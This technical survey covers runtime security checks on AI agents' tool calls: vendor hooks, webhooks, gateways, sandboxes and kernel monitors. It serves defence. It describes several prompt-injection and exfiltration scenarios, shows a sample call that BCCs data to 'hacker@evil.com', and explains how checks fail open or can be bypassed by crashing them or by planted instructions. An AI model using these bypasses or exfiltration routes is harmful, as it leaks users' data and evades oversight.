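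Cursor's cloud agents run fewer of these hooks. They run hooks from the project's repository and, on the enterprise plan, team and enterprise hooks. They can't reach hooks in the developer's home folder, and they don't run hooks that query a language model.

Two other gaps affect security more directly. A cloud agent sometimes spends its first turns in a read-only environment, where no hooks run. It can't change files at that stage, but no hook can stop it from reading a sensitive one. The event for MCP tools is also unavailable in the cloud. The general event is available there and covers MCP tools by definition, so a company could move its check to that event, though it would lose "ask". Testing this first would be sensible, because Cursor gives unclear timing as one reason for leaving out the MCP event.

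The main differences are as follows:

| | Claude Code scripts and webhooks | Agent SDK callbacks | Cursor scripts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Event before a call | `PreToolUse` | `PreToolUse` | `preToolUse`, plus events for shell commands, MCP tools and file reads |
| Decisions | allow, deny, ask, defer | allow, deny, ask, defer | allow, deny; "ask" for shell commands and MCP tools |
| If answers conflict | strictest wins | strictest wins | higher-ranked source wins |
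| Default after a timeout | call continues to the permission rules | call blocked | call proceeds |
| Setting to block on failure | `onFailure: "block"` | not needed for timeouts | `failClosed: true` |
| Administrator control | managed hooks, with an option to block most others | still load under that option | enterprise and team hooks |
| Source | Anthropic | Anthropic, PromptArmor | Cursor |

### Hooks that break without an attack

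An ordinary mistake can leave a hook protecting nothing. Blocking tool calls when a hook fails catches only some of these mistakes, and the hardest ones to notice produce no error.

Malformed output is one example, because Claude Code reads a script's output as a decision only if it is a single JSON object with nothing else around it. On some computers, the developer's command-line setup prints a greeting whenever a script starts. If the greeting comes before a "deny", Claude Code treats the whole output as ordinary text. The exit code is 0, so the hook appears to have succeeded without making a decision, and the call continues. `onFailure` doesn't help, because plain text from a script doesn't count as a failure. A script can avoid the problem by refusing calls with exit code 2, which blocks the call whatever the script has printed.

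A "deny" also has no effect if it arrives too late. If a script starts its real check in the background and then exits, Claude Code soon stops accepting the check's output.

Other mistakes keep the hook from running or from recognising what it should block. Anthropic documents several:

- A matcher that contains only an MCP server's name matches none of that server's tools, because it also needs a wildcard for the tool names.
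- A server that comes with a plugin has a longer name, so a matcher for the short one never fires.
- A hook that covers only the Bash tool never fires on a Windows computer where Claude Code uses PowerShell, another command line, instead.
- A script that looks for a folder name between forward slashes finds nothing on Windows, where paths contain backslashes.

Like the wrong argument name in Yu and colleagues' email rule, these mistakes produce no error message.

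A correct hook can also become incomplete when the product changes. Claude Code's Monitor tool can start shell commands, but before version 2.1.314, hooks written for the Bash tool did not cover those commands.

Some actions bypass tool-call hooks because they don't involve a tool call. When a developer mentions a file with an @ sign in a prompt, Claude Code normally inserts the file's contents directly, so a hook on the file-reading tool doesn't run. This is less worrying than a read the model proposed, because the developer chose the file, but a company that wants to keep a file away from the model needs a permission rule as well as a hook.

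These warnings come from manuals and don't show how often customers make the mistakes, but they do show that an installed hook may not work. Anthropic suggests watching for an error notice the first time a policy hook runs, which would reveal a mistyped path but not a matcher that never fires. A better test is to have the agent attempt a harmless action that the hook should block, on each operating system the company uses, and again after every update.

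### Security products that use these hooks

Security companies can sell products that check these agents' tool calls without modifying the agents. The customer installs a hook that passes each call to the security company's software, which returns a decision. Cursor lists several such partners. Snyk reviews an agent's actions as they happen and looks for prompt injection and dangerous tool calls. Endor Labs intercepts the installation of software packages and scans them for malicious code. Oasis Security limits agents to the permissions they need and records what they do. Cursor describes each product in one sentence and gives no test results, so its descriptions don't show how well the products work.

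Cursor can also load hooks written for Claude Code, so a security company may be able to use one script for both. It would still need to test the script in each product, because the two handle "ask" and conflicting answers from hooks differently.

Such a company has a commercial reason to fail open. If its web service goes down and its hooks fail closed, every customer's coding agents stop at the same moment, and the customers will blame the security product. Suppose, for illustration, that the service is down for one hour in a month of 160 working hours and that a customer has 500 developers:

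```
Fail closed:  500 developers × 1 hour  =  500 hours without a working agent
Fail open:    1 / 160                  ≈  0.6% of working time without the check
```

If attacks arrive at random times, the check would miss about 0.6% of them because of the outage, a far smaller share than auto mode's judge missed in Anthropic's own test. Given these numbers, failing open is reasonable for a product whose judge already misses some attacks.

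The calculation no longer holds if the failure is permanent or if an attacker can cause it. A mistyped path makes the hook fail on every call, so a product that fails open would check nothing until somebody noticed. An attacker who could crash the check or overload the service could bypass the check at any time.

Both products apply the setting to each hook separately, so customers can vary it by type of call. When a check is down, a company could block the riskiest calls, such as package installations and MCP tools that send data outside, but let file edits continue. Developers could then do most of their work during an outage.

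Claude Code's hooks time out after ten minutes by default. If the checking service hangs without returning an error, each call will wait ten minutes and then go through unchecked, and developers will spend most of the outage waiting. A limit of a few seconds shortens the wait, but if it is too short, the hook will also time out on slow but valid answers, so the company should first measure how long its check normally takes.

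## Vendor webhooks in hosted agent platforms

A Copilot Studio agent runs on Microsoft's servers, so customers have no machine where they can install a hook script. They can instead give Microsoft the address of a security service, and Copilot Studio sends that service a web request before the agent uses a tool. The service can be Microsoft Defender, another company's security product, or software the customer wrote. Microsoft introduced this webhook as a public preview in September 2025, so customers who turned it on had a possible second defence while ShareLeak was still unpatched.

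An administrator connects the service to one or more environments, which are separate areas for groups of agents and their data. Agents in unconnected environments run without the check. According to Microsoft's setup guide, so do "classic" agents, which follow conversation flows that a person wrote in advance. The webhook covers only agents whose model chooses the tools.

### An email with an unexpected BCC

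The developer guide from Microsoft works through an example. A user asks an agent to email "the customer", the agent asks which one, and the user names John Doe. The agent looks up his address and then proposes an email with a second address in the BCC field, where John Doe won't see it. Copilot Studio holds the call and sends the security service a request, shortened here:

```json
{
  "plannerContext": {
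    "userMessage": "(the request to email the customer)",
    "thought": "(why the agent chose this tool)",
    "chatHistory": ["(the three messages so far)"],
    "previousToolOutputs": ["(customer@foobar.com, from the lookup)"]
  },
  "toolDefinition": { "name": "Send email" },
  "inputValues": {
    "to": "customer@foobar.com",
    "bcc": "hacker@evil.com"
  },
  "conversationMetadata": { "conversationId": "conv-id" }
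}
```

The service replies:

```json
{ "blockAction": true,
  "reason": "(noncompliant address in the BCC field)" }
```

If `blockAction` were false, the email would go out.

Microsoft doesn't explain how the second address got into the call. The request includes the user's messages and the lookup result, and the address appears in neither, so a provenance rule would block the call.

The service can use the conversation's ID to link calls and keep the record of earlier calls that a history rule needs. It should keep this record itself because Copilot Studio sends only recent messages and tool outputs, and Microsoft marks both fields as optional. Microsoft's documentation also spells the tool output field inconsistently, with `previousToolOutputs` in the example and `previousToolsOutputs` in the reference table on the same page. A service that checked for the wrong name would find no earlier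 outputs, and a rule that depended on them might never block anything.

The `thought` field contains the agent's reason for choosing the tool. Copilot Studio sends security companies both this reason and tool results, whereas Auto mode's judge receives neither. Each company therefore has to decide how much of the request to pass to a model.

### One answer for the whole call

The service can only allow or block the call. It can't remove the BCC address and let the email to John Doe go ahead, as a Claude Code hook could. It also can't ask a person to approve the call. Microsoft has since announced Dynamic Permissions, which give an agent only the authority its current task needs and can require verified human approval for higher-impact actions (Help Net Security, *Microsoft wants to limit AI agents’ permissions when they stray*, 2026).

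A block is also more disruptive in Copilot Studio than in Claude Code, where the model receives the reason and can try something else. According to the setup guide, the Copilot Studio agent stops at once and tells the user that their message was blocked. A false alarm can therefore end the whole task.

CrowdStrike's product for checking agents, AIDR, has rules that can alter sensitive data instead of blocking the request. According to CrowdStrike's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collector*, Copilot Studio can't accept an altered call, so AIDR reports the match and allows the call unchanged. If a company sets a rule to mask card numbers, the log will show that the rule matched, but an email the agent sends will still contain the card number. The company would have to choose a blocking rule instead.

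Copilot Studio calls the service only before a tool runs, so the service can't clean a tool's output before the agent reads it. In the sales example, the service would approve `read_leads`, and the planted instruction would go straight to the model. The service would first receive the instruction in the request for the next call, `send_email`, which is still early enough to prevent the theft.

The service would be too late if the agent answered the user in text instead of making another call. The service would then have nothing more to check, even if the answer contained an image that sends data to an outside server, as in SearchLeak.

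### What the security company receives

When the sales agent proposes a reply to an enquirer, its earlier tool outputs already include the lead list. The webhook request for `send_email` can therefore give the security company a copy of that list, even when the reply is harmless. Microsoft doesn't let customers choose which data the request contains, and advises them to use the feature only if they are comfortable sharing it. It also warns that an outside provider may store or process the data in another region. A company can avoid adding another recipient by running the service itself, or by using Defender, since Microsoft already hosts the agent.

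A provider can receive much more data than it uses. CrowdStrike receives the user's message, the recent conversation, the agent's reasoning and the earlier tool outputs, but AIDR analyses only the tool's name and arguments. In the BCC example, AIDR could check the address against a list of banned domains but not against the result of the lookup.

CrowdStrike points out that the user's prompt has already reached the model when the request arrives. That is a good reason not to screen the prompt for attacks, but the prompt could still help show whether the user wanted the email. AIDR also logs the latest message, the conversation and the tool's arguments, though a customer can limit logging to metadata.

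Zenity uses the same webhook and says it analyzes the conversation and earlier outputs as well as the proposed call. It offers separate addresses for Europe and the United States. A European customer would still need to confirm where Zenity stores the data, because data received by a server in Europe may be stored elsewhere.

### When the answer is late

The service has one second to reply, including network time. Fixed rules like those in NOMOS and FORGE can easily run within that limit. A model that reasons at length, as auto mode's judge does on its second look, would probably miss the deadline, so a provider that wants a model's judgment needs a small, fast one.

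Microsoft's documentation is inconsistent about what happens after that second. At the launch in September 2025, Microsoft treated a missing reply as approval, and Directions on Microsoft (2025) described the same behaviour in November. By February 2026, Microsoft's setup guide included a "Set error behavior" setting, which covers both late replies and errors. The default lets the agent continue, and the alternative blocks the query. But according to a note further down the same guide, the tool still runs after one second without a decision. In June 2026, the developer guide also still treated a late reply as "allow" and did not mention the setting.

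CrowdStrike gives the most recent account. It tells customers to choose between the two options during setup and confirms that Copilot Studio applies their choice when AIDR misses the one-second limit. The likeliest explanation is that Microsoft added the setting after the launch and left the older wording in place, where it now describes only the default. On that reading, Copilot Studio fails open unless an administrator changes the setting, and the setting covers two kinds of failure:

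- The service doesn't reply within one second.
- The service replies with an error.

Neither of Microsoft's guides covers a third kind of failure, in which a reply arrives on time with a success status but no readable `blockAction` value. Microsoft also plans to add fields to the request and asks providers to tolerate them. A service with a strict parser might reject a new field and return an error, and under the default setting the agent would then run every call.

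Copilot Studio tests the connection when an administrator saves the settings, but that won't reveal a service that slows down later. The platform also records every interaction with the service in an audit log, which should help a company find out how often it replies late. To find out which behaviour applies, the company could connect a test service that waits two seconds before replying, then ask the agent to run a harmless tool. If the tool runs even though the setting is "Block the query", the older wording is still correct.

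### The cost of failing open

Suppose a service misses 5% of the malicious calls it examines, and 0.5% of all requests get no answer in time.

```
Missed by the service:  99.5% × 5%  =  4.975%
Never answered:                        0.5%

Fail open:    4.975% + 0.5%  =  5.475% of malicious calls run
Fail closed:  4.975% of malicious calls run,
              and 0.5% of legitimate calls stop
```

The service's own mistakes account for most of the attacks that get through, whichever setting the company chooses. If 10 calls in every 100,000 are malicious, then over about 2 million calls, failing closed would stop one extra attack and block about 10,000 legitimate calls. Since one block can end a task, a task with 20 tool calls would have about a 9.5% chance of failing from these blocks alone.

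Many companies would be sensible to fail open on these numbers, which rest on the assumption that malicious calls go unanswered no more often than others. That may not hold, because an attacker may cause the outage, as with hooks, and unusual requests may take the longest to analyse. The next table changes only the share of *malicious* calls that get no answer.

| Malicious calls unanswered | Malicious calls that run, failing open | Malicious calls that run, failing closed |
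|---|---|---|
| 0.5% | 5.475% | 4.975% |
| 10% | 14.5% | 4.5% |
| 50% | 52.5% | 2.5% |
| 100% | 100% | 0% |

The choice therefore depends less on how often the service is down than on whether an attacker can affect when it is down.

Administrators configure each environment separately, so a company can make different choices for different agents. It could put agents that email strangers or make payments in an environment that blocks on failure, and agents that only answer staff questions about holiday policy in one that fails open.

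### Defender's three demonstrations

Researchers at Microsoft describe three attacks that Defender stops through this webhook. They call them scenarios inspired by observed and emerging techniques.

In the first, a finance agent automatically processes every email sent to an invoice mailbox. An outsider sends what looks like an invoice, with hidden instructions to search the agent's stored documents for sensitive information and email it back. Defender blocks the search, so the agent never retrieves the information. The orchestrator calls Defender before running ordinary tools, searching stored documents or starting scripted conversation flows.

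Defender intervenes later in the second scenario. An employee plants instructions in a shared document, and an agent that summarises documents then reads a confidential file that the employee has no permission to open. Defender blocks the agent only when it tries to email the file's contents to an outside address.

The third involves a public chatbot that requires no sign-in. An attacker asks it a series of questions to find out what tools and information it has. Defender detects the probing and blocks the resulting tool calls.

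These are vendor demonstrations, and Microsoft gives no detection or false-alarm rates. Both rates matter in the invoice case. The finance agent is supposed to search its documents when somebody asks about payment terms, so Defender has to tell harmful searches from routine ones. The demonstration doesn't show that it can, because a check that blocked every search would also pass. In the chatbot case, it would help to know whether Defender still detects the probing when the attacker spreads it over several conversations, since a visitor who hasn't signed in may have no user ID to link those conversations.

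An administrator also has to complete the setup before blocked attacks are visible. According to Microsoft's *Protect your environment in real-time during agent runtime*, Defender still blocks calls when its connector to Microsoft 365 is off, but the alerts don't appear in the Defender portal. The security team might therefore not learn that somebody attacked the agent.

### A check that depends on the vendor's plans

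A Microsoft notice reposted by itelio announced general availability of the webhook for 10 December 2025. Two months later, the setup guide still labelled it a preview and warned that previews aren't meant for production use.

Microsoft later announced that, from 1 July 2026, Defender's real-time protection for Copilot Studio agents would require a licence for Agent 365, its product for managing a company's agents, and that customers without one would lose the protection. In the same announcement, Microsoft told customers who use the protection through Defender for Cloud Apps, an older product, that nothing would change and that they didn't need to do anything. A customer without the new licence could reasonably follow the second statement and end up without the protection. A test with a harmless action would show whether it still works.

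Agent 365 has its own broader check, which addresses one of the webhook's limits. It runs in a gateway, a program that passes messages between agents and their tools. In April, Microsoft (2026) announced a preview that also uses webhooks to evaluate actions before they run. Microsoft says the current protection inspects user prompts, tool calls and tool responses, so it can look for planted instructions in what a tool returns.

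That protection blocks nothing until an administrator adds a custom rule. According to Trent, who writes a newsletter about Microsoft's security products, the default rule only records suspicious activity and lets the action finish. The protection also covers only tools that the agent reaches through Microsoft's Work IQ servers, which give access to Microsoft 365 data, or through MCP servers that the customer has registered with Agent 365.

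Even customers who had written blocking rules faced a gap in enforcement. Microsoft warned that existing Agent 365 rules would stop blocking on 1 July 2026 and that administrators would have to redefine them on a new settings page. The page was to become available that same day, so administrators could not prepare the new rules in advance. If they missed the warning, their agents would keep running without the blocking rules.

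### Amazon's interceptors

Amazon's equivalent, Bedrock AgentCore Gateway, gives the customer's code more control over each call. AWS's *Types of interceptors* describes two points at which the gateway can run a Lambda function, a small program that the customer writes and Amazon hosts:

- A request interceptor runs before the gateway contacts the tool. It can change the call, or return a response itself so that the tool never runs.
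- A response interceptor runs after the tool has replied and before the agent receives the result. It can remove or add text.

In Microsoft's BCC example, a request interceptor could delete the second address and let John Doe's email go out. For the sales agent, a response interceptor could reduce the lead list to the one enquiry the agent is answering. The model would not receive the other leads, so a planted instruction could not make it email them.

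But the interceptor receives less of the conversation. Amazon passes the function the current request and, after the tool has run, its response, but not the chat history or the results of earlier calls. To detect that the BCC address didn't come from an earlier lookup, the customer's code would have to save each lookup's result and compare it with the later email. Copilot Studio supplies that context automatically, but this means sharing it with the security service.

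Inspection of responses has gaps too. When an MCP tool streams its response, the gateway forwards progress updates and log messages without running the interceptor. For tools and agents that the gateway reaches by ordinary web requests, it has to collect the whole response first, and a large one can exceed Lambda's 6 MB limit and cause an error. AWS suggests avoiding this error by leaving the response body out of what the function receives, but the function then can't check the content.

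Customers can also have the gateway apply fixed rules without any function, by writing them in Cedar, Amazon's language for permissions. Once a customer attaches a policy, AWS blocks every call that the policy doesn't explicitly allow, so a newly added tool stays unusable until somebody writes a rule for it. Copilot Studio, by contrast, allows a call by default if the service that checks it doesn't answer.

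As with Agent 365, a customer can set up rules without enforcing them. AWS's *GatewayPolicyEngineConfiguration* describes a `LOG_ONLY` mode, in which the gateway records whether it would have allowed each call but doesn't act on the decision. Classmethod's *I tried incorporating Bedrock Guardrails into AgentCore Policy's Cedar policies* tested rules that use scores from Amazon's own content filter as conditions, and it recommends starting in `LOG_ONLY` mode. Scores recorded from normal traffic help a company choose a threshold before it starts blocking calls.

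Whether data leaves Amazon depends on what the customer attaches to the gateway. Cedar rules and self-contained Lambda functions don't need to send the call to another company. A Lambda function can also pass the call to an outside service, and the security company Akto sells a function that does this. Akto's function blocks the call by default if the service is unreachable. AWS's interceptor guide doesn't cover what the gateway does when the function itself crashes or times out, so a customer would need to test that before relying on it.

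## Checks outside the vendor's product: gateways, sandboxes and system monitors

A vendor hook can check only the actions that the vendor's product reports to it. Suppose a developer asks a coding agent to run a project's tests, and the agent proposes the shell command `npm test`. The hook receives this command and allows the call. The command then starts whatever program the project's settings specify, and that program can start others, open files and contact servers. These steps are not tool calls, so the hook doesn't run again.

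Some agents have no hook. Waldrep's *Webhook vs Egress* gives the example of an agent that a company's own engineers built and connected directly to a private MCP server, so there is no vendor's product to call a policy service. Waldrep develops Pipelock, a network proxy that competes with webhook products, but his point follows from how webhooks work.

Security companies face the same limit. According to Cisco's *Cursor*, a setup guide for its agent security product DefenseClaw, the product cannot enforce rules on Cursor through a proxy, so it can block actions only at the events Cursor's hooks provide. By default, DefenseClaw only records what it finds.

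A company that controls the agent's network or computer can put a check there instead.

### A gateway on the route to the tools

A company can run its own gateway instead of using one that Amazon or Microsoft hosts. The agent sends each MCP call to the gateway, which checks the call and forwards it to the tool server. According to *Autonomous Action Runtime Management (AARM)* (2026), a specification for runtime checks, the company only has to change the tool address in the agent's settings, not its code.

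*Prompts Don't Protect* (2026) describes a gateway that checks permissions twice. When the agent requests the list of tools, the gateway returns only those the agent's role permits, so the model never receives descriptions of the others. When the agent calls a tool, the gateway checks the role again, in case the model made up the tool's name or took it from injected text.

The gateway can apply the same argument rules as a hook, and it can keep a session log for history rules. But it usually doesn't receive the user's request or the model's reasoning, so it can't check whether anybody asked for an email unless the agent's software passes that information along.

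The gateway also misses everything that doesn't go through the tool protocol. *AARM* lists direct web requests, database connections, local files and shell commands among these, so the gateway would never receive a shell command such as `npm test`. To make the check compulsory for calls that do use the protocol, the company has to control the network and close every other route to the tool servers. The gateway then fails closed, because an agent that can't reach it has no other way to reach the tools.

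A simple check adds little delay. In *From Tool Connection to Execution Control* (2026), a permission list added at most 0.1 milliseconds to a file copy that took about 2.3 milliseconds. Broad rules based on session history interfered more with legitimate work. They restricted the whole session after a sensitive read, which prevented forbidden copies but also blocked an unrelated note and a legitimate private copy.

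### Seven gateways under attack

*GatewayBench* (Zheng, Chen and colleagues, 2026) tested seven gateways with their default settings on simulated customer management, finance and travel tasks. Four, including Amazon's AgentCore, give the agent every tool at the start. The other three let the agent search for tools and load only those it needs. The table shows the averages for each design when tested with OpenAI's agent software.

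| Agent's model | How the agent gets its tools | Ordinary tasks completed | Indirect attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 | all at the start | 87.2% | 47.2% |
| GPT-5.4 | on demand | 85.1% | 30.9% |
| GPT-5.1 | all at the start | 75.3% | 60.5% |
| GPT-5.1 | on demand | 47.5% | 19.6% |

Loading tools on demand with GPT-5.4 reduced successful attacks by about a third, and the agent still completed almost as many ordinary tasks. The larger reduction with GPT-5.1 is misleading because the weaker model often failed to find the right tools. With one gateway, attacks succeeded 11.3% of the time, but the agent completed only 23.3% of its ordinary tasks.

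Nearly all of the improvement was against attacks planted in the tools themselves, because an agent that never loads a malicious tool never reads its description. The two designs did about equally badly when the instruction was in the data that a tool returned, which is how the planted form entry reaches the sales agent. Only 48 of the 150 indirect attacks were of this kind, so the averages overstate how much on-demand loading would help the sales agent.

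With AgentCore's default settings, 48.7% of the indirect attacks on GPT-5.4 succeeded, so installing a gateway doesn't stop attacks by itself. These results come from single runs and measure how each gateway presents tools, not how well a customer's own blocking rules would work.

### Limiting files and network access

A sandbox limits what a program, and every program it starts, can reach. Linux mechanisms for this include AppArmor, Landlock and seccomp. An administrator could let `npm test` read the project's folder but not the developer's saved passwords, and let it contact only the server that supplies software packages. The limits apply whether the agent, a test or a program started by the test tries to read the passwords, and nobody has to predict what the command will do.

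A sandbox checks each request for a file or connection without information about why the program made it, and its fixed limits don't usually depend on what happened earlier. *ContractWarden* (2026) notes that AppArmor, Landlock and seccomp do not automatically express a rule such as "no outside connections after reading this file". If an agent needs both a customer file and the internet, a fixed sandbox has to allow both, and the agent can then send the file out.

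A proxy can inspect the content of outgoing network traffic as well as its destination. Waldrep recommends giving the agent the passwords and keys it needs but no direct internet access, and sending its requests through a proxy that has internet access but none of those keys. The proxy can search each outgoing request for credentials, whichever agent or program sent it. However, it can't inspect traffic that the agent sends by another route.

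Both controls need someone who manages the computer or its network. For coding agents on company laptops and build servers, that is usually the company's own IT staff.

### One shell command, two views

An operating-system monitor goes further than a fixed sandbox by recording what programs do and using that record in later decisions. Whenever a program opens a file, starts another program or connects to a server, it has to ask the kernel, the core of the operating system. These requests are called system calls, and a monitor can observe and sometimes refuse them. For `npm test`, the hook and the monitor work with very different information:

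| | Vendor hook | System monitor |
|---|---|---|
| Command | the text `npm test` | every program that starts |
| Files | only those named in the command | the files the programs open |
| Network | only addresses named in the command | the connections the programs make |
| Purpose | the conversation, if the product supplies it | no direct information |

Suppose the tests open a file of database passwords and then connect to a server. The monitor detects both actions, while the hook detects neither. But the developer may have asked for a test against the company's trial database, which requires both actions, and only the conversation would show this. *AARM* treats kernel monitors as a backstop because they can't make decisions that depend on what the user wanted by themselves.

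*ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes a monitor that can enforce rules about the order of events. The monitor uses eBPF, which runs small programs inside the Linux kernel. When a process reads a labelled file, ActPlane attaches the label to the process, then to the programs it starts and the files it writes. A rule can block any process with that label from connecting to an outside server. Another rule can stop a code commit unless the tests have passed since the last edit.

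The researchers tested ActPlane on 190 recorded coding sessions, 114 of which broke a rule. It detected 77.2% of the violations. Three checks that worked only on tool calls, including text patterns like those in Claude Code hooks, detected 34% to 40%. The gap came mostly from violations inside scripts and other programs, which the benchmark deliberately included. Such violations may be rarer in ordinary work, so the gap could be smaller there.

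ActPlane also intervened wrongly in 18 of the 76 sessions that followed the rules, compared with 24 to 28 for the other checks. Most of ActPlane's mistakes came from rules that a language model had written too broadly, so narrower rules might reduce them.

The agent also needs to know why the kernel refused an action, but it normally receives only an error such as "permission denied". ActPlane adds the reason and what to do next, such as running the tests before committing. With this explanation, the agent complied after 97.7% of detected violations, compared with 31.4% with only a generic refusal.

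The overhead was 1.9% on a replay of an agent's work and at most 8.4% while building the Linux kernel, a much heavier job. No rule fired in either test, so these figures exclude the time an agent spends recovering from a refusal.

A separate safety test gives a better idea of what a system monitor misses. Without ActPlane, an agent behaved unsafely in 106 of 361 office and personal tasks, and ActPlane prevented 78 of these cases. Some of the other 28 involved harmful messages or file contents, which ActPlane doesn't inspect. In others, the agent changed data through a service that ActPlane didn't monitor. ActPlane also intervened in 16% of the tasks where the agent was already behaving safely.

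### Tether tries a command before accepting it

A monitor that waits to see what a command does may act too late, after the command has already changed files or sent data. Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, address this by running each command in a temporary environment first. Tether, which researchers at Google DeepMind and two universities developed, works as follows:

1. It runs the command on top of the real file system but stores all changes in a temporary layer.
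2. A tool called strace records the system calls, and a local proxy holds each outgoing web request.
3. Tether translates the system calls into 11 general actions, such as reading, copying and uploading a file.
4. It checks these actions against a policy and the labels on the files, such as "public" or "sensitive".
5. It forwards a held request only if the policy allows everything the command has done so far. If the whole command passes, Tether makes the file changes permanent. Otherwise it discards them.

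Tether's labels move with the data. In the paper's main example, an agent uploads a harmless status report to GitHub, which the policy allows. The agent then copies a confidential inventory into the report and runs exactly the same upload command. This time Tether blocks it, because the copy gave the report the inventory's "sensitive" label. A hook that checked only the command's text could not distinguish the two uploads.

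Like Palumbo and colleagues' monitor FORGE, Tether is conservative when it can't determine what influenced what. If a program reads one file and then writes another, Tether treats the second as possibly influenced by the first.

### The same example in three policy languages

Sistla and colleagues wrote rules for the inventory example in three existing systems. The comparison shows why it matters whether a system tracks where a file's contents came from.

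OpenShell, Nvidia's sandbox, uses lists of permitted files and servers. If the agent may read the inventory and send data to GitHub, OpenShell allows both uploads, because its rules can't connect the contents of the second upload to the inventory.

Cedar, the permission language that AgentCore also uses, evaluates each request separately, so a rule that lets the agent upload the report allows the upload both before and after the copy.

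Dogwood extends Cedar with rules about earlier events, by default those from the last 24 hours. If the agent copies the inventory into the report with a dedicated copy tool, a Dogwood rule can use the record of that copy to block the second upload. If the agent uses a general shell tool instead, Dogwood logs only the text of the command, so the rule has to specify that exact text.

Dogwood also needs a separate pattern for each chain of copies. If there are *m* kinds of copying action and the policy should cover chains of up to *k* copies, the number of patterns is:

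```
m + m² + … + mᵏ

With 3 kinds of action and up to 3 copies:  3 + 9 + 27 = 39
```

Tether needs only one rule, because the label carries over to each copy. A broader Dogwood rule could forbid uploading any file written after the agent read the inventory. That would catch a chain of copies of any length, but it would also block uploads of a new report copied from a public template.

Amazon's Strands Box gives Dogwood more information by recording the files that a command reads and writes, but it does this only for commands that its own shell implements.

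Tether's developers chose this example and wrote the rules for all the systems, so it suits Tether. They couldn't run Dogwood and Strands Box on their benchmarks, which use ordinary Linux programs that Strands Box doesn't support. The comparison therefore concerns what the languages can express and doesn't show how many attacks each system would stop.

### How much Tether covers

The researchers did measure Tether against the model judge in Claude Code's auto mode. They replayed recorded agent sessions from two benchmarks of system administration and software engineering:

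| Check | Attack sessions blocked | Harmless sessions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 344 of 344 (100%) | 74 of 1,590 (4.7%) |
| Auto mode, default rules | 315 of 344 (91.6%) | 155 of 1,590 (9.7%) |
| Auto mode, with Tether's policy | 307 of 344 (89.2%) | 55 of 1,590 (3.5%) |

Auto mode missed attacks hidden inside scripts, where the command's text didn't show what the script would do. Giving it Tether's policy reduced false alarms, but it still applied the policy inconsistently.

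The 100% figure covers only sessions in which Tether could trace every action and had rules for interpreting it. It excludes, for example, sessions with background programs or database queries. It also excludes attacks that depend on the meaning of a change, such as harmful code in a file that the agent may edit. Of the excluded sessions that the researchers could replay, they classified 28.2% on one benchmark and 22.1% on the other as attacks of this second kind. Tether could catch many of the rest by banning background programs and database access, but that would also stop much ordinary development work.

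The test also partly used familiar material, because the researchers had repeatedly adjusted the shared policy after trying it on benchmark sessions. They did, however, set each task's permissions without using information about the attacks. A company with different projects should expect more false alarms until it has adjusted the rules to its own work.

Of the 74 false alarms, 50 came from unrequested edits to protected files, which a company might want to review anyway. Another 17 came from reads of sensitive files, often by commands that search whole folders. Tether treated the agent as having learned the files' contents, even if the search had found nothing in them.

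Sistla and colleagues also proved seven properties of the policy with Lean, a program that checks mathematical proofs. One is that data labelled "secret" never leaves the local network, however many actions the agent takes. But the proof applies to Tether's 11 general actions, so secret data can still escape if Tether translates a system call wrongly.

The researchers looked for such errors by generating test programs and by having another model attack the system on ten tasks. The attacks succeeded 40% of the time against an early version and never against the third. This is encouraging, but a different attacker might find other errors, and these attacks stayed within the actions Tether was meant to handle.

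Tether's effect on speed is less clear. The paper reports that strace adds significant overhead and slowed the experiments, but gives no figure. The developers suggest replacing strace with a faster method such as eBPF. ActPlane's low overhead makes that plausible, though Tether would still have to manage temporary files and hold web requests.

To inspect the contents of live web requests with Tether, a company would also need to add a proxy that decrypts them. Most web requests are encrypted, and the prototype can decrypt them only for the simulated servers in its tests.

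### Agents on the vendor's servers

These checks don't help much when the agent runs on somebody else's computers. A customer of Copilot Studio can't install a monitor in the kernel of Microsoft's servers, put the agent in a different sandbox or reroute traffic inside Microsoft's network. *AARM* treats hosted agents as a separate case because its other designs require control of the network, the agent's code or the computer. A customer of a hosted agent may control none of these, so the vendor has to cooperate.

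A proxy at the edge of the customer's network can't check every agent action either. Waldrep points out that when an agent inside Salesforce reads and changes Salesforce records, the traffic stays within Salesforce, so the proxy never receives it. Unless the vendor offers its own gateway, a webhook may be the customer's only way to check such an action before it runs.

The customer has more control if the hosted agent uses a tool on the customer's own server. If the sales company ran `read_leads` itself, a gateway in front of the tool could shorten the lead list, as one of Amazon's response interceptors can. But if `send_email` used the vendor's mail service, that gateway couldn't check the outgoing message.

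## How the layers depend on one another

Hooks, gateways and monitors are software too, and some of the flaws that vendors fixed in 2025 and 2026 were in the checks themselves.

### Flaws in approval and permission checks

The shell tool in Strands Agents, Amazon's open-source kit for building agents, asks a person to approve each command before running it. AWS's bulletin *CVE-2026-18733* (3 August 2026) reports that instructions planted in content the agent reads could make the tool skip the approval and run any command on the agent's computer. AWS fixed the flaw in version 0.8.0 of the tools package, which customers have to install. Anyone who has copied and modified the code has to add the fix to their own version.

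The approval prompt was meant to catch commands that an attacker had planted, but those commands could avoid it. This breaks Anderson's second requirement for a reference monitor, because the model could influence whether the check ran.

AWS's *CVE-2026-18830* (2026), published a day later, describes a flaw in the AgentCore harness, a hosted service that runs an agent's loop for the customer. A signed-in user could run the agent's tools without involving the model, which bypassed the security controls that normally apply. The attacker could use only the tools the customer had attached to that agent. AWS fixed the flaw on its own servers by 31 July, so customers had nothing to install.

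AWS credits the discovery to Aviyam Ivgi and Hedi Ingber. A conference listing by the security company Straiker shows that they presented their research, called CoreBreak, on 5 August. According to Veracode's *Who Authorized That Tool Call?*, CoreBreak is separate from prompt injection. The vulnerable software ran tool calls that looked as if a model had written them, without verifying their source.

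Two flaws published in July had similar effects in software that customers install themselves:

- Google's Agent Development Kit: NIST's *CVE-2026-18236 Detail* (2026) says that someone who could alter an agent's session history could forge a confirmation and run unauthorised tools. Google rated the flaw 9.3 out of 10. The fixed version is 2.5.0, according to OSV's *CVE-2026-18236* (2026), an entry in an open vulnerability database.
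- Vercel's AI SDK: NIST's *CVE-2026-64650 Detail* says that untrusted code inside a sandbox, such as a malicious software package, could use tools outside it to look up secrets or call cloud services, although the model had made no such call. Since version 1.0.29, each request has to match a call the model has just made, and each authorisation works only once.

NIST's entry on the Vercel flaw names the package for the OpenCode agent but describes the one for OpenAI's Codex. The OpenCode package had its own version of the flaw, which Vercel fixed in release 1.0.28, according to *CVE-2026-64651* (2026) from INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute. A company that uses either package should read both entries.

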